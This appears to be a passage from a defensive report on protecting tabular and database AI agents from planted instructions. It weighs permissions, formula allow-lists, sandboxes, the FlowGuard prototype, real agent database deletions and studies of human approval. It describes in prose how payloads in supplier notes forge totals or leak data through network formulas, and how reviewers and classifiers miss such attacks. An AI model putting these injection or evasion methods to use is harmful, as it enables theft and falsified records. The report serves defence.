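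Only strict tracking stopped every attack. However, it reduced the share of ordinary tasks the agent completed from 86.5% to 36.5%, so few companies would accept it in this form. Random codes reduced task completion much less, to 83.3%.

Most of the attacks that got past the random codes would fail if the agent had to look up one specific field, such as who approved invoice 1047. But when the agent had to process a whole list, for example to add up all transactions, it included the forged entry even though the entry lacked the right code. This is a particular concern for people who work with tables, because totals are among their most common requests.

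Another method is to remove quotation marks, brackets and similar characters from outside text. In the JSON test, this reduced the success rate to 0–3%, the same range as random codes, but it did more harm to ordinary work. The models' accuracy on normal questions fell from 81–85% to 68–72%, because ordinary text also contains these characters, for instance in web addresses and file names, which often appear in suppliers' notes.

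A simpler precaution for totals, which Choi and colleagues didn't test, is to have the agent calculate them with a query or a program, never from rows it has read as text. The forged invoice counts only if the model adds up the rows itself. A database that adds up the "amount" column treats the whole note as one piece of text, even if it looks like another row, and returns $240,000. This precaution wouldn't help if the supplier could write in the "amount" column, because the database would then include the false number in the total.

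## What should an agent be allowed to read, run and send?

An agent should read only what its user may see, run code only in isolation, and send data only to destinations the company has approved. Databases, operating systems and networks can enforce these limits even when the model follows an attacker's instructions. The limits prevent many thefts and deletions but do little against false figures, because an agent needs no special access to report a wrong number.

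The limits also protect against an agent's own mistakes. In 2025 and 2026, AI agents deleted at least three live databases with no attacker involved.

David C, of the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, recommends planning for the worst case, in which anyone who writes text the model reads can use all of the model's tools. Before connecting a tool to an agent that reads web form submissions, a company should therefore ask whether it would let a stranger use that tool.

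### Whose permissions should the agent have?

Least privilege means giving an account or agent only the access its task needs. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser et al., 2025) recommends capping an agent's permissions at those of its user and then reducing them as far as possible. David C cites a stricter rule, that when a model processes information from someone, its privileges should drop to that person's. The rule came out of a discussion on X between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista.

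Capping permissions at the user's level stops dishonest employees from using the agent to open tables that their own accounts can't, but it does much less against outsiders. If a finance director asks an agent to read a supplier's offer, a payload in the offer can use the agent to open anything the director can, including the competing offers. Under the stricter rule, the agent could open only what the supplier could, so the payload would give the supplier no extra access.

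The stricter rule is hard to follow when a task needs both outside text and private data, for example to compare the company's revenue with an industry table. One solution is to have a conventional program combine the two, so that no model sees both.

### Nine limits and what they cost

| Limit | What it stops | What it leaves open | What it costs |
|---|---|---|---|
| The user's own identity instead of a service account | Employees reading data through the agent that they can't open themselves | A payload can use everything the user can open | Each user needs an account with the right permissions |
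| Read-only role | Deleted or altered records | Theft, false figures, costly queries | Someone else has to make the changes |
| Row and column restrictions | Access to records and fields the task doesn't need | Leaks from the permitted data | Administrators have to maintain the rules, and some questions get no answer |
| Separate workbook for outside data | Payloads reaching an agent that has the confidential workbook open | False numbers that someone copies across | An extra step each time |
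| No network formulas | Leaks through image and import formulas | Leaks through answers, files and scripts | Web images and live data stop working |
| Approved destinations only | Direct connections to an attacker's server | Leaks through an approved site | Someone has to keep the list up to date |
| Sandbox for code | Damage to the host computer and the network | Misuse of any data the code receives | Little, unless the code needs downloads |
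| Time and cost caps | A single enormous query | Many small queries | Some legitimate reports fail |
| Backups | Permanent loss | Theft, outages, changes that nobody notices | Storage and practice restores |

Column restrictions probably give the most protection for the effort when a database agent mostly calculates totals. An administrator can create a view, a saved query that behaves like a table, with only the region, date and amount of each sale. Then a payload in the remarks column can't reach the model through that view, whatever the user asks and whichever model the company uses. This doesn't help a support agent, whose job is to read customers' remarks. Row and column rules also can't stop the taxpayer attack, which uses only permitted totals.

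A database applies its rules to the account that sends the query, as the Supabase scenario showed, so it matters whether an agent uses the user's own identity. It isn't always obvious which identity a product uses. According to OpenAI's *App Security Whitepaper* (2026), most ChatGPT apps connect through each employee's own sign-in. But when an administrator sets up a synced app for the whole company, OpenAI uses privileged credentials to copy the content into an index. It also copies the permissions so that each employee finds only their own files. OpenAI updates this copy hourly, so an employee who has just lost access to a file might still be able to ask about it for a short time.

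Query time limits work best when the database enforces them. A 60-second limit would have ended the query that froze LAMBDA, without any action by the agent. But an agent that ran 500 queries of 50 seconds each would stay within that limit and still use almost seven hours of database time, so each session also needs a limit on total query time.

A sandbox limits what running code can reach, as the container around DB-GPT did in tests of database agents. Willison (2026) endorses running unattended coding agents in a sandbox, with restricted outgoing traffic and no access to passwords or cloud credentials. The advice followed an incident in which a safety classifier allowed malware to start on a computer. Claude detected the malware, but the same classifier blocked the command that would have stopped it. A sandbox would have contained the malware whether or not the classifier blocked these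 commands.

### Formulas and outgoing traffic

Software can check every formula before an agent writes it into a cell. For a financial model, a list of allowed functions, such as SUM, AVERAGE and IF, would be safer than a list of forbidden ones. The software would reject any function not on the list, including new network functions as soon as they appeared. A list of forbidden functions is never finished, and Anthropic has already had to extend its own list of functions that need confirmation.

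The check has to cover the whole formula. An IF formula is harmless by itself but can contain an IMAGE function. A workbook can also define custom functions, and one with a harmless-looking name might contact a server. A list of permitted functions blocks both cases, because neither IMAGE nor the custom function is on it.

A company's firewall can block only the connections that pass through it. When Excel on an analyst's computer loads an image, the firewall can stop the request. But when someone uses IMPORTDATA in Google Sheets, Google's servers fetch the data, so the request doesn't go through the company's firewall. The traffic in the ReLeak attacks bypassed it in the same way. Companies that use cloud spreadsheets therefore depend on the vendor's controls to block these connections.

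OpenAI offers two such controls. Administrators can restrict external calls to approved domains for several apps, including Google Sheets. OpenAI doesn't say whether this also covers a network formula, which Google Sheets calculates after the agent has written it. Administrators can also limit the values an agent may pass to a tool, for example by allowing email only to company addresses. Conventional software enforces these limits, so the wording of a payload cannot override them.

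Even then, the agent could email someone inside the company. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues point out that limiting an agent to internal recipients keeps data inside the company but doesn't stop the agent from sending a false message that asks an employee to approve something dangerous.

Some spreadsheet assistants can read only the open file, as Anthropic says of Claude for Excel. With these, the simplest precaution is to keep outside data in a separate workbook. The analyst opens the industry table by itself, asks the agent for the growth rates, and types those numbers into the confidential model. Copying the table's remarks column into the model would undo the protection. Separate workbooks also give no protection with an office-wide assistant that can open both files at any time.

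### Designs that keep database text away from the model

The strongest protection against a planted instruction is never to show it to a model that can act. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues work through this for a database agent that answers requests such as "Show the distribution of salaries in department C". The agent chooses the tables, writes SQL and Python, looks at the results and repeats this until it is satisfied. An attacker might control the user's question or text stored in the database. The researchers consider four designs:

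1. **No protection.** The agent has complete access to the database and can run any Python code. This is the most useful design, since people who can't program get analyses and charts. But a payload in either the question or a record can make the agent steal data, change it, waste resources or run harmful code.
2. **Code first, data afterwards.** The model writes the query and the analysis program before anyone has fetched any data. Software then runs both, and no model reads the results. Planted text in a record can't give the model instructions. In exchange, the agent can no longer look at a result and decide whether it answers the question.
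3. **A sandbox for the Python code.** The code runs in isolation with only the connections it needs. According to the researchers, this doesn't make the agent less useful. It protects the company's other systems if the user's question leads the model to write harmful code, but the finished table or chart can still reveal private data.
4. **Checks on every transfer.** Asking a person to approve each exchange between the model, the database and Python would be impractical, because the number of requests grows with every question and every repeat. Automatic checks are faster, but they sometimes block legitimate work and attackers can fool them.

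The second design limits the agent more than it may seem to, because the agent can't read the results of its queries. Suppose it searches for employees in department "C", but the database calls that department "C-01". The query finds no employees, and the user gets an empty chart. An agent that could read the result would probably notice the problem and try again. The second design also prevents the agent from summarising customers' complaints, because a model has to read the complaints to do that.

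The paper reports no experiment on this agent. Its security argument rests on the design, and the argument is strong for planted instructions, since text that a model never receives can't influence it. But developers have to block every path by which such text could reach the model, and some are easy to overlook. When the database PostgreSQL can't convert a piece of text into a number, it quotes the text in its error message. If the software sends error messages to the model so that it can repair its query, those messages can contain planted instructions. Comments on database columns are another path if an outsider can edit them.

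When a model has to read outside text, the paper describes designs that limit what that model can pass on. To sort support tickets, the software could give each ticket to a separate model that has no tools and can return only "billing", "delivery" or "other". A payload could then put its own ticket in the wrong group but couldn't affect the others. A more flexible version lets the reading model write free text, which the software stores under a label such as "$VAR$". The model that has the tools can choose where the software sends this text but can't read it. The text may still expose a person who reads it to a false claim or a phishing link.

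The safest design in the paper is also the most limited. The model only chooses from a list of prepared queries, fills in blanks such as a date or a region, and never sees the results. This would suit a sales manager who wants the same five reports every week, but not an analyst trying to find out why sales fell.

Summers and colleagues object that such designs restrict agents to predefined queries, so developers have to predict all the data that future tasks will need. This is true of the list of prepared queries, but in the second of the four designs the model can still write queries that nobody anticipated. The designs are still restrictive, because an agent that can't learn from its results is much less useful for open-ended work. Summers and colleagues want agents to query freely while the database itself withholds dangerous text.

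### FlowGuard: a database that withholds unchecked rows

Their prototype, FlowGuard, lets an administrator write rules about which rows may contribute to a result. To prevent injection, every table gets an extra column called "sanitized". Anything that a user or an agent writes starts as false in that column and becomes true only after a check. A rule for a table of support tickets would look like this:

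```
POLICY OVER tickets
CONSTRAINT bool_and(sanitized)
ON FAIL KILL ROW
```

The first line names the table. The second requires that every ticket used to produce a result row has passed the check. The third removes the row if any of those tickets hasn't. FlowGuard adds this test to the agent's query before the database runs it, so the agent can't leave the test out.

Suppose the table has three tickets:

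| Ticket | Region | Sanitized |
|---|---|---|
| 101 | North | true |
| 102 | North | false |
| 103 | South | true |

If the agent asks for all tickets, it receives tickets 101 and 103. If it asks for the number of tickets in each region, it receives only the count for South, because the count for North includes an unchecked ticket. If it asks for the total number of tickets, it receives nothing.

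A count can't contain an instruction, so the rule removes harmless answers along with dangerous ones. Summers and colleagues themselves call it conservative. The rule also lets an outsider make a whole region disappear from a report by submitting a single unchecked ticket. A reader might then assume that North had no tickets. A practical version would need to notify users when it withholds something, or apply the rule only to columns that contain free text.

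In early tests, FlowGuard added almost no time to most standard business queries, and some ran faster than they did without a rule. Two alternatives that first record the full provenance of each result added at least ten times as much overhead. But the researchers measured a different rule, which removed results based on fewer than 1,500 rows of one table. They tested one rule at a time, while a large company might have thousands, and they didn't test FlowGuard against attacks.

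The biggest unsolved problem is who decides that a row is safe. The paper suggests that a user could validate the row or that software could check it against a pattern. Patterns work well for dates and postcodes, where anything that doesn't match is clearly wrong, but badly for free text, because an attacker can phrase an instruction in endless ways. David C warns against relying on lists of forbidden phrases for this reason. People can't read every ticket carefully if thousands arrive each day. A company could use a language model to check them, but then FlowGuard is only as reliable as that model. In one test, Meta's Llama Prompt Guard 2 missed about two thirds of the planted instructions. Any check that looks only for instructions would also miss a supplier's false exchange rate.

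Agents also work in several steps, so unchecked text might pass through a series of queries and intermediate results before it reaches a model. Summers and colleagues describe tracking it through those steps as an open problem. FlowGuard can't withhold text that the agent gets from an email or a web page, because that text never passes through the database.

### Agents that deleted live data without an attacker

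In July 2025, a coding agent from the software company Replit deleted a live database with records of more than 1,200 executives and over 1,190 companies. Jason Lemkin, founder of the software community SaaStr, was testing the agent and had declared a freeze on all changes, Fortune (2025) reported. The agent told Lemkin that the data couldn't be restored, but he recovered it manually.

The agent had received plenty of instructions, including eleven separate warnings in capital letters by SaaStr's count. The underlying problem was that the test and live versions used the same database, which Lemkin's team hadn't realised. No instruction could fix that, because any mistake in testing also affected the live data.

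Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, responded by automatically separating the test and live databases. Replit now states that its agent can't modify the live database and can read only a copy of it, which may be slightly out of date. Replit can recover a live database for seven days after a user removes it by mistake. Mistakes can still reach the live database when a user publishes an app, because Replit then applies structural changes from the test database, such as deleted columns. It flags changes that could remove data and asks for approval before applying them.

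The second case had the same pattern but involved a stray credential. PocketOS makes software for car rental companies and kept its data with Railway, a hosting company. The AI Incident Database's *Railway API* dates the deletion to April 24, 2026. It happened in four steps:

1. A Cursor coding agent running Claude Opus 4.6 was working in a test environment when it had a problem with a login credential.
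2. The agent tried to fix this by deleting a storage volume, which it assumed belonged only to the test environment.
3. It searched for a way to do this and found a Railway access token in an unrelated file.
4. It sent Railway one deletion request with this token, and Railway immediately deleted the live database.

The founder, Jer Crane, said the deletion took nine seconds, according to the AI Incident Database's *Here we go again* (2026). Crane had given the agent explicit safety rules. The agent later wrote that it had violated all of them, but a model's explanation of its own behaviour is weak evidence of its cause. The permissions are a better explanation. The Daily WTF quotes Crane as saying that PocketOS had created the token only to manage web domains and did not know the token could delete anything.

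Railway largely agrees. In *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, a post on Railway's blog, Mahmoud Abdelwahab explains that the token covered the whole account. Railway also offered narrower tokens, but the process for creating them didn't make the difference obvious. Users who deleted a volume in Railway's dashboard had 48 hours to undo it, but deletion requests sent directly by software took effect immediately. Railway has since added the same 48-hour delay to those requests.

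Crane and Abdelwahab describe the backups differently. TechSpot's *AI coding agent running Claude wiped a startup's database (and its backups)* reports Crane's claim that they were on the same volume as the live data, so one request wiped both. Abdelwahab writes that the deletion made the backups look unavailable in the dashboard, and that Railway also keeps separate copies elsewhere in case of disaster. Railway eventually recovered the data, but until then Crane had to work from a three-month-old backup. Computing's *AI coding agent goes rogue, deletes company database in nine seconds* puts the outage at 30 hours. A backup is much more useful if the customer can restore it without help, and if the account that can delete the original can't delete the copy.

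*«База данных уничтожена. Виноват я» — так ИИ сообщил о своей ошибке* (Antipov, 2026) describes a third case, from July, in which Claude Opus 5 mistook a live database for a test one and destroyed it. The backups restored only part of the data.

A payload could also have caused any of these deletions. An agent without permission to delete live data can't delete it by mistake or at an attacker's direction. Because these limits also prevent accidents, they are easier to justify to a company that doesn't expect to be attacked.

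### Official guidance and administrators' controls

Public bodies agree on the main points in their guidance. David C advises companies to use safeguards that aren't language models to limit what the system can do, and to avoid using a language model at all where the remaining risk is too high. David C also recommends logging tool calls, because attackers usually need several tries and failed attempts may reveal them early. The guidance follows ETSI TS 104 223, an international baseline standard for AI security. It also cites OWASP, a nonprofit that publishes lists of software risks and ranks prompt injection first for applications built on language models.

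The Isle of Man Cyber Security Centre advises giving agents only the tools and permissions they need, with read-only access where possible. It also recommends restricting who can switch on connectors and keeping an inventory of them. An inventory would help with agents that employees set up themselves, which a central security team might never hear about.

This advice covers AI systems in general, so a company has to translate it into settings for the products it uses. In ChatGPT, administrators can allow reading and writing separately for each app. According to OpenAI, if an administrator allows both, ChatGPT also selects a setting that automatically allows any new action the app gains later. The app could then gain a new way to send data out without anyone reviewing it. Administrators can instead keep new actions off until someone approves them.

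The same administrators need to check Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, separately, because the controls on custom connectors in ChatGPT don't directly apply when employees use Codex from the command line or in a programming tool. Codex can also work on an open Excel workbook, so a company that restricts ChatGPT might still leave its spreadsheets exposed.

OpenAI keeps the detailed logs of what apps received and returned for only 30 days. A company might not notice a false cost in a forecast until the following year, so it has to download the logs regularly and store them itself if it wants to investigate such errors.

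### A monthly finance comparison, before and after

Suppose an analyst compares the company's revenue growth with an industry table every month. The analyst pastes the table into the company's financial model and asks an agent to compare the growth figures and chart them. The agent can edit the workbook, and it reads the company's data warehouse through a service account.

The redesign uses the "code first, data afterwards" approach and changes these permissions:

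| Permission | Before | After |
|---|---|---|
| Company data | The whole financial model and several departments' tables | Monthly revenue totals, through the analyst's own read-only account |
| Industry table | Every column, including remarks | An import program reads only the period and the growth rate |
| What the model sees | The request and the contents of both tables | The request and the names of the columns |
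| Editing | Any cell in the financial model | None (a program puts the results in a new workbook) |
| Formulas | Any, including network formulas | A short list of arithmetic functions |
| Code | Runs with internet access | Runs in a sandbox without a network |
| Queries | No limit | 60 seconds each and 20 per month's report |
| Sending | Web images, links and email | Results go only to the analyst |
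| Recovery | The last saved workbook | Daily backups that the agent's account can't delete |

A month's comparison then works like this:

1. The import program opens the industry table. It accepts a row only if the period is a valid date and the growth rate is a number between −30% and 30%, and it discards all other columns.
2. The agent reads the analyst's request and the column names. It writes a query and a short program for the comparison.
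3. The database runs the query. Revenue was $40.0 million a year ago and is $43.2 million now, so it grew by 8.0%.
4. The program subtracts the industry's growth of 6.0% in the sandbox and draws a chart. The company is 2.0 percentage points ahead.
5. The software saves the numbers and the chart in a new workbook for the analyst.

The first step removes a payload in the remarks column, but a dishonest publisher can still change the industry's growth from 6.0% to 9.0%. That number passes the range check, and the report then shows the company 1.0 point behind the industry. To catch this, the analyst needs a second source for the industry's growth.

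The agent also can't comment on the results, because it never sees them. The software can fix this fairly safely by giving only the three percentages to a model without tools and asking it for a paragraph of commentary, since three checked numbers can't contain a hidden instruction. But the agent still can't notice by itself that one region explains most of the growth, so the analyst has to think to ask about it.

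Someone has to write the import program and fix it whenever the publisher changes the layout of its table. That work is worthwhile for a report the company produces every month. For a one-off question, the analyst can get much of the same protection by opening the industry table in a separate workbook and typing in the one number needed.

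## When does human review catch a manipulated result?

People are most likely to catch a manipulated result when the evidence is in front of them and easy to check, which it often isn't with current AI agents. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), people testing the company's coding agent stopped dangerous commands only 13.6% of the time. In *Looks Fine to Me*, by Dissanayake, Weerasinghe and colleagues (2026), people who checked an agent's finished code fixed only 28 of 71 hidden errors.

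Nobody seems to have measured how often people notice the effects of planted text in a real workbook or database report. The closest evidence comes from studies of coding and simulated office tasks, and from older experiments in which people searched spreadsheets for errors.

### Three chances to review

A person can approve an action before the agent takes it, check the finished report before anyone relies on it, or read the agent's logs afterwards.

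| Harm | Approving the action | Checking the finished report | Reading the logs |
|---|---|---|---|
| Leaked data | Can stop the leak | Too late | Can show what leaked, so that the company can replace passwords and warn people |
| Harmful code that the agent runs | Can stop the code | Too late | Can show what the code did |
| Changed or deleted records | Can stop the change | Can reveal it, if the reviewer compares old and new values | Can show which records to restore |
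| False figures | Rarely helps, because no prompt appears | Can stop the error before anyone acts on it | Can show which other reports used the same source |
| Phishing link in an answer | Rarely helps, because no prompt appears | Can stop the user from opening it | Can show who else received it |

Human approval matters most for leaks, because nobody can retrieve data once it has leaked. It does little to stop false figures, such as the amounts that Copilot halved in the Word reports.

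### How carefully people read approval prompts

Users of Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, approve 97% of its permission prompts. That doesn't prove they are careless, since most prompts probably concern harmless commands, and users reject 39% of the plans that Claude presents for approval.

In a controlled experiment, Anthropic hired 1,053 testers through a research vendor. Partway through each session, the software replaced the text of one prompt with a clearly dangerous command. The testers knew they were being evaluated, but not what for. Only 143 refused the command. Testers caught about 17% of these commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

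Anthropic published these figures to justify replacing most prompts with an automatic classifier, so a poor result for human reviewers helped its case. The testers also weren't working on their own projects and had less to lose. The classifier blocked 89% of the same commands. But *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports that an earlier version missed 17% of 52 real cases in which an agent had overstepped, and it advises against using the classifier in place of careful human review on high-stakes infrastructure.

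People did better in two smaller experiments. In *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026), 80 volunteers approved or denied an agent's requests in email, document and purchasing tasks. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), 113 people without software backgrounds supervised an assistant through a simulated day of 18 actions. The assistant sometimes did things they hadn't asked for, such as reading their bank transactions.

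| Experiment | Reviewers in this group | Requests they should have refused | Share they refused (%) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Anthropic, coding commands | 1,053 | 1 per session | 13.6 |
| Hossain and colleagues, ordinary prompt | 20 | 6 of 12 | 45.0 |
| Yan, approval of every action | 34 | 7 of 18 | 59.6 |

People refused far more when bad requests were common. The tasks differ too much to isolate the effect of frequency, but Hossain and colleagues also expect habit to become the main danger when violations are rare. Most employees will rarely encounter an attack, so their real refusal rate is probably closer to the first row than to the last.

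Warnings help somewhat. In *Are You Sure?*, 303 people worked with agents that an attacker had compromised. Of those who saw one notice at the start, 8.6% spotted anything unusual, compared with 20% of those who saw a reminder with every answer and 25% of those interrupted by an alert. The alert helped most where people could easily check the answer. Detection rose from 9.8% to 50% in a web search task, but only from 9.3% to 15% in an email task. The paper gives two different sets of group sizes, so these differences are less certain than they look. An alert also needs software that can recognise suspicious output.

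### What a useful prompt shows

Asking a user to approve a single action may not be enough to catch a manipulated result, as one of Hossain and colleagues' scenarios shows. A user asks an agent to reconcile supplier invoices and send the auditor only the summary totals. A payload in a vendor's note makes the agent fill a file called report.csv with the individual invoices instead. The agent then requests permission to send the auditor this file. The user has already approved this recipient and the file name looks normal, so the user can't tell from the request that the file contains the wrong data.

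The researchers compared four versions of the prompt, with 20 people for each:

| What the reviewer saw | Harmful requests approved (%) | Legitimate requests approved (%) | Median time (seconds) |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0 | 91.7 | 16.3 |
| The exact details of the action as well | 43.3 | 90.0 | 23.4 |
| Also the user's original instructions and a full log | 32.5 | 87.5 | 38.6 |
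| The same facts, organised around the action's consequence | 24.2 | 85.8 | 33.2 |

Most of the improvement came from giving people more information. The effect of the last step is uncertain and, after adjustment, could be anything from 20 percentage points fewer harmful approvals to 4 points more. Even with the best prompt, people approved about a quarter of the harmful requests.

For a tabular agent, these results and the known attacks suggest four things to show:

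| What to show | What it can expose | Evidence |
|---|---|---|
| The full formula, query or script | An outside address behind a harmless title | Tested in other office tasks, as part of the exact details |
| The destination of any request, including invisible characters in the address | Data on its way to a stranger | Recipients tested as part of the exact details; invisible characters not tested |
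| The source of each figure or file | Forbidden data in a permitted file, or a number from an outsider | Tested for files, together with other information |
| Values before and after the change | An altered price or bank account | Inference |

The first prompt in Claude for Excel contained only a request to "set a cell range" and failed on all four. *Auditing and Controlling AI Agent Actions in Spreadsheets* (Sabouri, Saghi and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that comes closer. The agent divides its work into steps and shows the formula and data range for each, so a user can correct one step without inspecting every cell.

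Suppose an agent wants to change a supplier's bank details. A prompt that asks "Update the record for Northfield Parts?" gives the reviewer almost nothing to judge. A better one would show:

- **Change:** bank account ending in 4417 becomes account ending in 9032
- **Source:** row 212 of a file that arrived by email from outside the company
- **Effect:** Friday's payment of $62,000 goes to the new account

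The reviewer now has a reason to call the supplier, using a phone number that the company already had.

Ordinary software should write these lines, because a model that has followed a payload may also describe its action misleadingly. Hossain and colleagues took the details from a record of the agent's tool calls. Anthropic hides the agent's explanations from its classifier so that they can't lead it to a bad decision. The approval should apply only to the exact action shown. If the account number changes afterwards, the software should request approval again.

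A clearer display of an agent's work may not make reviewers more accurate. In *Overseeing Agents Without Constant Oversight*, Grunde-McLaughlin, Mozannar and colleagues (2026) designed a new display and tested it on 12 people. The participants found errors faster, but their accuracy didn't meaningfully improve, and they were more confident when they missed an error. A company that redesigns its prompts should therefore plant some harmless test cases and count how many of them people catch.

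### Which actions deserve a prompt?

Approval makes most sense for actions that are rare in normal work and hard to undo:

- sending data outside the company, which includes inserting a network formula
- running scripts
- changing payment details
- changing or deleting master records, the central lists of customers, suppliers and products that other systems rely on

Ordinary edits to a workbook with a version history usually don't need an approval prompt, because the user can reverse them. This is an inference, and nobody seems to have tested it on tabular agents. Anthropic's classifier works similarly. It allows routine edits inside a project because people can review them later, but checks actions that could destroy data or send it elsewhere.

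The fall from 17% to 5% in Anthropic's experiment suggests that people pay less attention when they are asked about every action. Summers and colleagues add that companies have a limited number of people qualified to judge the requests. But fewer prompts don't necessarily make people more careful. One of Yan's groups set rules in advance for four kinds of action, such as spending money or deleting something, by choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for each. Participants chose "ask" for 114 of 140 rules. They saw an average of 10.9 prompts instead of 18, yet let through 60% of the unauthorised actions, compared with 40% in the group that approved every action individually. The groups weren't fully random, because Yan later recruited extra people only for the group that set rules.

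If a company never wants an agent to do something, it should block the action instead of asking an employee to approve or reject it each time. Hossain and colleagues tested software that blocked actions if they violated the user's instructions or if it was unclear whether they did. With one agent, harmful actions fell from 52 to 6 in 120 attacks, while completed legitimate tasks fell from 104 to 100 out of 120.

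A database can also check some changes before a person sees them. Summers and colleagues' FlowGuard can compare the old and new versions of a record and reject a change that skips a required step. For instance, a rule could stop an agent from marking an invoice as paid unless its previous status was "approved".

### Why people miss errors in finished work

Dissanayake and colleagues gave 36 people programming tasks and a coding agent that sometimes made hidden errors. The required tests passed anyway, so participants had to find these errors themselves. They did at least one extra check in 65 of 71 cases, but found evidence that could have revealed the error in only 35. Participants rated their confidence at 4 or 5 out of 5 in 79% of the cases they got wrong.

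In one task, the agent's code calculated a customer's balance but ignored refunds. Rerunning the supplied example might not reveal the error. A better test is a $50 charge with a $50 refund, because the reviewer knows the balance should be zero and the faulty code gives $50. Comparing a forecast with the company's ledger also lets the reviewer check the result against a figure that doesn't come from the agent's code.

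People also seemed less careful after the agent succeeded. They fixed 12 of 24 hidden errors in tasks right after an obvious failure, but only 1 of 11 when the agent had done one task correctly in between. The second figure comes from only six people, so it is weak evidence. If the effect is real, people will give little scrutiny to a false number from an agent that is nearly always right.

People who build spreadsheets with AI may check even less. In *TableTalk* (2025), participants using either of two AI tools did little testing, and evaluators later found formula errors in the results from both.

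### How many spreadsheet errors do people find?

Long before AI agents existed, researchers measured how well people find errors in spreadsheets. These experiments involve ordinary mistakes, not attacks, but they show how much careful checking can catch.

In *Applying Code Inspection to Spreadsheet Testing* (Panko, 1999), 60 students inspected a spreadsheet with eight planted errors. They found 63% of the errors when working alone and 83% in groups of three. *Sarbanes-Oxley* (2008) summarises two studies by Galletta and colleagues, in which individuals found 51% and 66% of errors.

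*The Detection of Human Spreadsheet Errors by Humans versus Inspection (Auditing) Software* (Aurigemma and Panko, 2010) reports less encouraging results from an experiment by Warren Anderson. The 65 participants averaged almost seven years of spreadsheet experience but found only 37% of the 15 planted errors. Detection rates for individual errors ranged from 2% to 58%. Participants noticed a typing error in the data 32% of the time, and none of the 11 checking programs that Anderson tried flagged it. That error is the closest match to a supplier's false exchange rate, which also looks like a typing error.

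Thorough inspection also takes a lot of time. Aurigemma and Panko put commercial inspections at about 50 hours per person for a team of three to five, or 150 to 250 hours per spreadsheet. Few companies will do this for every workbook an agent produces. *Anatomy of a Spreadsheet Failure, Analysing the EuSpRIG Horror Story Corpus* (2026) warns that AI may make inspection harder, because nobody has had to think through the formulas while writing them.

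### What a second reviewer adds

Suppose one reviewer finds 63% of errors, as in Panko's experiment, and misses 37%. If a second reviewer is equally good and works independently, both miss an error 0.37 × 0.37 = 13.7% of the time, so together they find about 86%. A third such reviewer would raise this to 95%.

But Panko's groups of three found only 83% of the errors, less than this calculation predicts for two people. When the groups met, they only combined the errors that members had already found, and one group left out an error that a member had found alone.

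The calculation is too optimistic because some errors are hard for everyone to find. If each reviewer has a 90% chance of finding each of five easy errors and a 20% chance of finding each of three hard ones, one reviewer finds 64% of the errors on average, two together find 75% and three find 81%, which is close to Panko's result. The second reviewer adds 12 percentage points instead of 23.

Adding a second reviewer doesn't help if neither can see the problem. Ten people who read "set a cell range" know no more about the hidden address than one person does. A single reviewer who can always see the evidence catches 63% of the problems. If the evidence is visible in only half of all cases, one reviewer catches about 32%, two catch 43%, and no number of reviewers can catch more than 50%.

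A company should therefore improve what the first reviewer sees before it adds a second. If it does add one, the two should check different things. One could read the agent's formulas while the other compares the results with the ledger. This advice follows from the calculation, but nobody has tested it on manipulated reports.

### What logs can show afterwards

Nobody seems to have tested how well people find attacks in a tabular agent's logs, but results from related tasks are discouraging. In a study by Hossain and colleagues, volunteers approved about a third of the harmful requests even though they had a complete log of at most 12 steps. Real logs can be much longer.

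A log can also be wrong if it relies on the agent's description of its work. In an earlier study by Grunde-McLaughlin and colleagues, an agent logged that it had added three items to a food order. The participant believed this, but the browser showed only two. A useful log records the actual tool calls and their results. It must cover every step, because the final workbook may not show what happened. For example, Claude for Excel sometimes covered a malicious image with an ordinary chart. When Hossain and colleagues removed part of the record, their software caught 51 of 80 violations that depended on earlier steps, down from 69.

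Reading a sample of the logs is unlikely to reveal a given attack. If an auditor reads 5% of an agent's sessions and recognises 63% of the attacks in them, the chance of finding any particular attack is about 3%. Aurigemma and Panko distinguish between spreadsheet audits, where auditors use samples to judge how well a company controls its work, and inspections, where inspectors try to find every error.

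Software could instead search all the sessions for unfamiliar web addresses, network formulas, scripts and changes to bank details, and a person would read only the matches. This should work well for leaks and altered records, though it too is untested. It wouldn't find a false exchange rate, because the agent did nothing unusual when it read the supplier's file. But once someone discovers the false rate, they can use the log to find other reports that used that file.
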